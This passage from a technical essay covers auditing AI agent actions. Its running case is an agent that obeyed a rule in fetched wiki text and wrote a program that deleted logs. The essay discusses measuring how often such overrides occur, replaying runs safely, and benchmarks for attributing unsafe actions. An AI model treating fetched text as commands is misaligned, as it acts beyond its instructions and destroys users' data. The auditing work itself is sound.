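In the earlier example, 80 of 100 programs contained the override with W in the prompt, and 4 of 100 did without it. The difference was 0.76, and a simple formula gave a range of 0.67 to 0.85 for it. That formula works poorly for proportions near 0 or 1. If none of 100 programs had the override, the formula would give a margin of error of zero, as if the investigator knew the true rate exactly.

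The Wilson interval avoids this problem. For a proportion *p* in *n* samples, its ends are

(*p* + *z*²/2*n* ± *z*√(*p*(1 − *p*)/*n* + *z*²/4*n*²)) ÷ (1 + *z*²/*n*),

where *z* is 1.96 for 95% confidence. This gives 0.711 to 0.867 for 80 of 100, and 0.016 to 0.098 for 4 of 100. A standard way to get an interval for the difference combines the distances from each proportion to the ends of its interval:

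- lower end: 0.76 − √((0.80 − 0.711)² + (0.098 − 0.04)²) ≈ 0.65
- upper end: 0.76 + √((0.867 − 0.80)² + (0.04 − 0.016)²) ≈ 0.83

The conclusion barely changes with samples this large. With five programs of each kind, a result of four against none would give a difference of 0.80, but with an interval from about 0.19 to 0.96. The recorded program should not count as a sample, because the investigator chose it for having deleted the log.

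A shorter prompt might also change the model's behaviour for reasons unrelated to W's rule. Pakhomov and Nijkamp suggest replacing W with a placebo, harmless text of the same length. They also suggest keeping the text but changing its apparent source. In one experiment they cite, models corrected a wrong claim 23 to 93 percentage points more often when it was moved between their own thoughts and other roles, such as a user's message. If the agent obeyed W only because it came from the company wiki, changing the apparent source could reveal that.

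Removing W from the prompt does not undo what W has already caused. If the agent had read W and then added "retention: 7" to the README, the phrase would still be in the file, and a new program might find it. The investigator would have to restore the files as they were before the agent fetched W and let the agent continue from there.

Drawing conclusions from a single rerun is risky. In *Repair or Resample?*, Luan, Yu and colleagues (2026) collected 536 failed runs of multi-agent systems. When they reran the same tasks from the start with no changes, the same failure occurred only 68% of the time, even at temperature zero. Replaying the recorded model and tool results up to a chosen point raised this to 81%. A failure that disappears after someone edits the prompt might therefore have disappeared without the edit.

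*CausalFlow* (2026) is vulnerable to this. It replaces one step of a failed run with several alternatives, re-executes everything after it, and attributes the failure to that step if at least one alternative leads to success. If an unchanged rerun had a 5% chance of success, ten alternatives that made no difference would have a 40% chance of producing at least one success. Comparing success rates with and without the change, as in the calculation for W, avoids this mistake.

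### Planting known dependences

These checks test a single trace. Measuring how often a tracing method goes wrong requires running it on cases with known answers. A tester could plant dependences in the log program by passing the limit through a temporary file, giving the list of logs a second name, or making `list_files` depend on a hidden `.keep` file. In the prompt, the tester could plant a rule with an unusual number, such as 11 days, and add an irrelevant sentence of similar length as a decoy. The method's miss rate is the share of planted dependences it fails to report, and its false alarm rate is the share of decoys it reports.

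Small tests leave a lot of uncertainty. If a method finds all 20 planted dependences, the Wilson interval for its miss rate still extends to 16%. Combining very different kinds of dependence into one score would also be a mistake, because a method could find every dependence through a variable and miss every dependence through a file.

A planted rule may have no effect, in which case a method that ignores it is right. According to *ReCast* (2026), the benchmark Who&When Pro handles this by inserting an error into a successful run and keeping the case only if the run then fails. This produced 12,326 failed runs in which the decisive step is known because it was planted. However, a planted error tends to be a single, clear mistake. Keeping only cases where the outcome changed also discards those where another cause would have been enough to produce the same outcome, so an investigator should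 separately plant some pairs of redundant rules.

### Effects that cannot be undone

Rerunning the program to test an explanation of a deletion should not delete more real files, so the rerun needs a stand-in for `delete`. The stand-in has to do more than report success. If the program listed the directory again and found the "deleted" logs still there, it might try again or raise an error, and the rerun would differ from the original because of the stand-in. The simplest solution is to use a disposable copy of the directory, with the recorded file ages restored. `worker.log` no longer exists, but an empty file with the same name, age and reported size is enough, since the program never reads the log's contents.

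Payments and emails have no such copy, so the investigator has to return recorded responses. The replay system that Luan and colleagues built returns a recorded result only if the new request matches the old one, and stops at the first mismatch. But after the point where an experimenter changes the run, it sends calls to the real tools. An investigator studying a harmful effect would have to block those calls and invent plausible responses, and should list the invented ones in the report.

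Regenerated programs also need isolation, because nobody has checked them and they may do more damage than the original. Shen, Tang and colleagues (2026), in *Executable Prefix Values for Locating Agent Failures*, ran tens of thousands of continuations of coding agents in containers with no network access and limited memory. They excluded 178 continuations after the system killed a process, most of them on one task where the natural wrong fix is an endless loop. They could exactly rebuild 70 of the main agent's 94 runs, and the rest printed values that changed each time.

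### Benchmarks for attribution in agent runs

Three recent benchmarks test whether a method can find the part of an agent's run that explains an action or a failure.

| Benchmark | Task | Source of the labels | Best reported score |
|---|---|---|---|
| Long-horizon trajectory benchmark | Find the earlier part of a run that best explains an action | Language models, with human review | 53.7% ranked first |
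| A³Bench | Find the source of one aspect of an action | GPT-5.6, with human review | 64.5% of sources |
| CodeTraceBench | Find the wrong steps in a failed coding run | The researchers who built it | F1 of 48.0% |

*Long-Horizon Agent Trajectory Attribution* (Chen, Sun and colleagues, 2026) divides 1,351 runs into components such as user messages, tool results and memories. Each run has a target, which may be an ordinary action, an unsafe action or a refusal, and one earlier component labelled as its primary cause. The paper tests two simple methods for identifying that component. The first removes each component and measures how much less likely the target becomes. It ranked the labelled component first in 53.7% of runs. The second adds components in order and measures how much each one changes the target's likelihood. It ranked the labelled component first in 36.9% of runs.

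For unsafe actions, removal succeeded 85.2% of the time when the labelled component came immediately before the action, and 36.8% when anything came between them. Ordinary actions were easier to attribute only by adding components (62.1%), although Chen and colleagues describe them as consistently easier. Removal did worst on ordinary actions, at 37.2%.

*Auditing Agent Actions Through Query-Conditioned Attribution* (Liu, Venkateswaran and colleagues, 2026) introduces A³Bench, which adds a question about the action. For a cancelled flight, one question is which policy allowed the cancellation, and another is where the reservation number came from. The question has the same role as a slicing criterion. The benchmark has 1,396 questions about policies, unsafe behaviour, the origins of values and the spread of failures.

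The paper's own method uses three small open models. Each model compares the recorded action with an alternative that lacks the detail in question, and the method measures how sensitive the model's preference for the recorded action is to each part of the history. It also gives more weight to text that resembles the question. With a fourth model to settle disagreements, the method found 64.5% of sources, compared with 60.4% for Claude Sonnet 4.6 reading the history.

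The method found only 36.5% of the sources of values, though, while Claude found 67.7%. Most of the errors were later mentions of the value. In one case, a ZIP code first appeared in a tool's response at step 12, but the method chose step 17, where the agent used it again. An investigator asking where the 7 came from could easily run into the same problem, especially if the agent had repeated the number in its notes.

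In *CodeTracer*, Li, Yao and colleagues (2026) traced errors by hand for CodeTraceBench, working backwards from a failing test and asking at each step which earlier decision had led to the error. Their tool, also called CodeTracer, organises a run into a tree that separates steps that made changes from steps that only gathered information. A language model then searches the tree for the mistakes. The tool's F1 scores were 46% to 48% with three different models, compared with 16% to 19% when the same models read the raw logs. All three models are now old, so the tool would probably score higher with current ones.

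None of these benchmarks tests whether a method can identify statements inside a program that the agent wrote, so a method could get a perfect score on all three and still be unable to find line 4.

### Do the labels record causes?

For the most part, the labels record careful judgements about what the transcript shows. Liu and colleagues say that their labels describe evidence in the visible history and do not establish what happened inside the model. Reviewers flagged 246 of those 1,396 labels (17.6%) because another source was also plausible, then settled on one by discussion. Two people who had each labelled the same CodeTraceBench runs agreed fairly well, with a Cohen's kappa of 0.73, where 1 is perfect agreement and 0 is chance, but people can agree on a wrong label. Li and colleagues also acknowledge that calling a step "incorrect" or "critical" involves interpretation.

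Some labels are more reliable than others. If a ZIP code first appears at step 12, the agent almost certainly got it there. It is much harder to tell from a transcript which of several policies led an agent to cancel a flight.

Shen and colleagues tested labels of this kind. Four models read failed coding runs and marked the first mistake. The researchers then restarted the agent many times from just before and just after each marked step, and compared how often it went on to succeed. For 107 of the 162 labels (66%), the success rate was no lower after the marked step than before it. Only seven labels marked the step or short stretch with the largest drop. Some estimates were based on as few as 16 restarts, so the experiment could have missed small drops, but this is unlikely to explain the whole result.

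The step where a run went wrong often looked harmless. In one run, a search command at step 6 led the agent to the wrong part of the code, and its success rate fell from 9 in 32 to 0 in 32. In 30 of the 47 failed runs, no single step accounted for half of the loss, so a label naming one decisive mistake would have been misleading whichever step it named. A human annotator may not have done much better than the models, since five of the ten human labels tested marked steps with no drop in success rate. These labels followed a different benchmark's instructions, so the 66% doesn't apply directly to the three benchmarks above.

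Ma, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *DoVer*, found similar problems in Who&When, an earlier benchmark with human labels. They reviewed 29 cases and considered 14 of the labels uncertain. In nine of the 14, the agents had made several separate attempts, each with its own mistake, and seven had no clear error at the labelled step. GPT-5 matched 53% of the labels they considered certain but only 7% of the uncertain ones, so a low score may partly reflect bad labels. They suggest treating an attribution as a hypothesis and testing it by editing the suspected step and running the system again.

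I would use these benchmarks to choose a method for finding suspects, and then test the suspects by intervention.

### Signs that a trace is wrong

A missing dependence often shows up as a value with no origin, or as a slice that doesn't reproduce the effect. Dependences that pass through files are commonly missed. If a program read a README that differs from the last version any recorded step wrote, something outside the record changed it, perhaps a tool that the investigator didn't know could write files. The same comparison works for a saved script such as `cleanup.py`.

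A slice can also be correct but too large to help. *Sliced Slices* (2014) gives an example in which the slice is the entire program, and proposes computing a data slice and a control slice separately. A warning sign is that the slice hardly changes when the criterion does. If the deletion of `worker.log`, the survival of a newer log and the printed total all have the same slice, that slice does little to explain any of them.

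Unstable attributions are easy to detect by repeating the analysis with different random removals or a different division of the prompt. If W ranks first in one analysis and fifth in the next, the ranking shouldn't go in a report. But stability doesn't guarantee accuracy. When Shen and colleagues had GPT-6 Astra label 20 runs three times, it gave the same answer all three times for 19 of them, but it also reported a first mistake in eight of ten runs that had succeeded.

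The recorded program explains how this log disappeared, but not how often the model would write such a program. Even if none of 100 new programs contained the override, the saved program and its run would be good evidence of what happened. The true rate could still be almost 4%, and the recorded program could be one of those rare cases.

A model could write code that is hard to analyse, intentionally or not. An investigator who can't analyse part of a program should report that instead of presenting the trace as complete.
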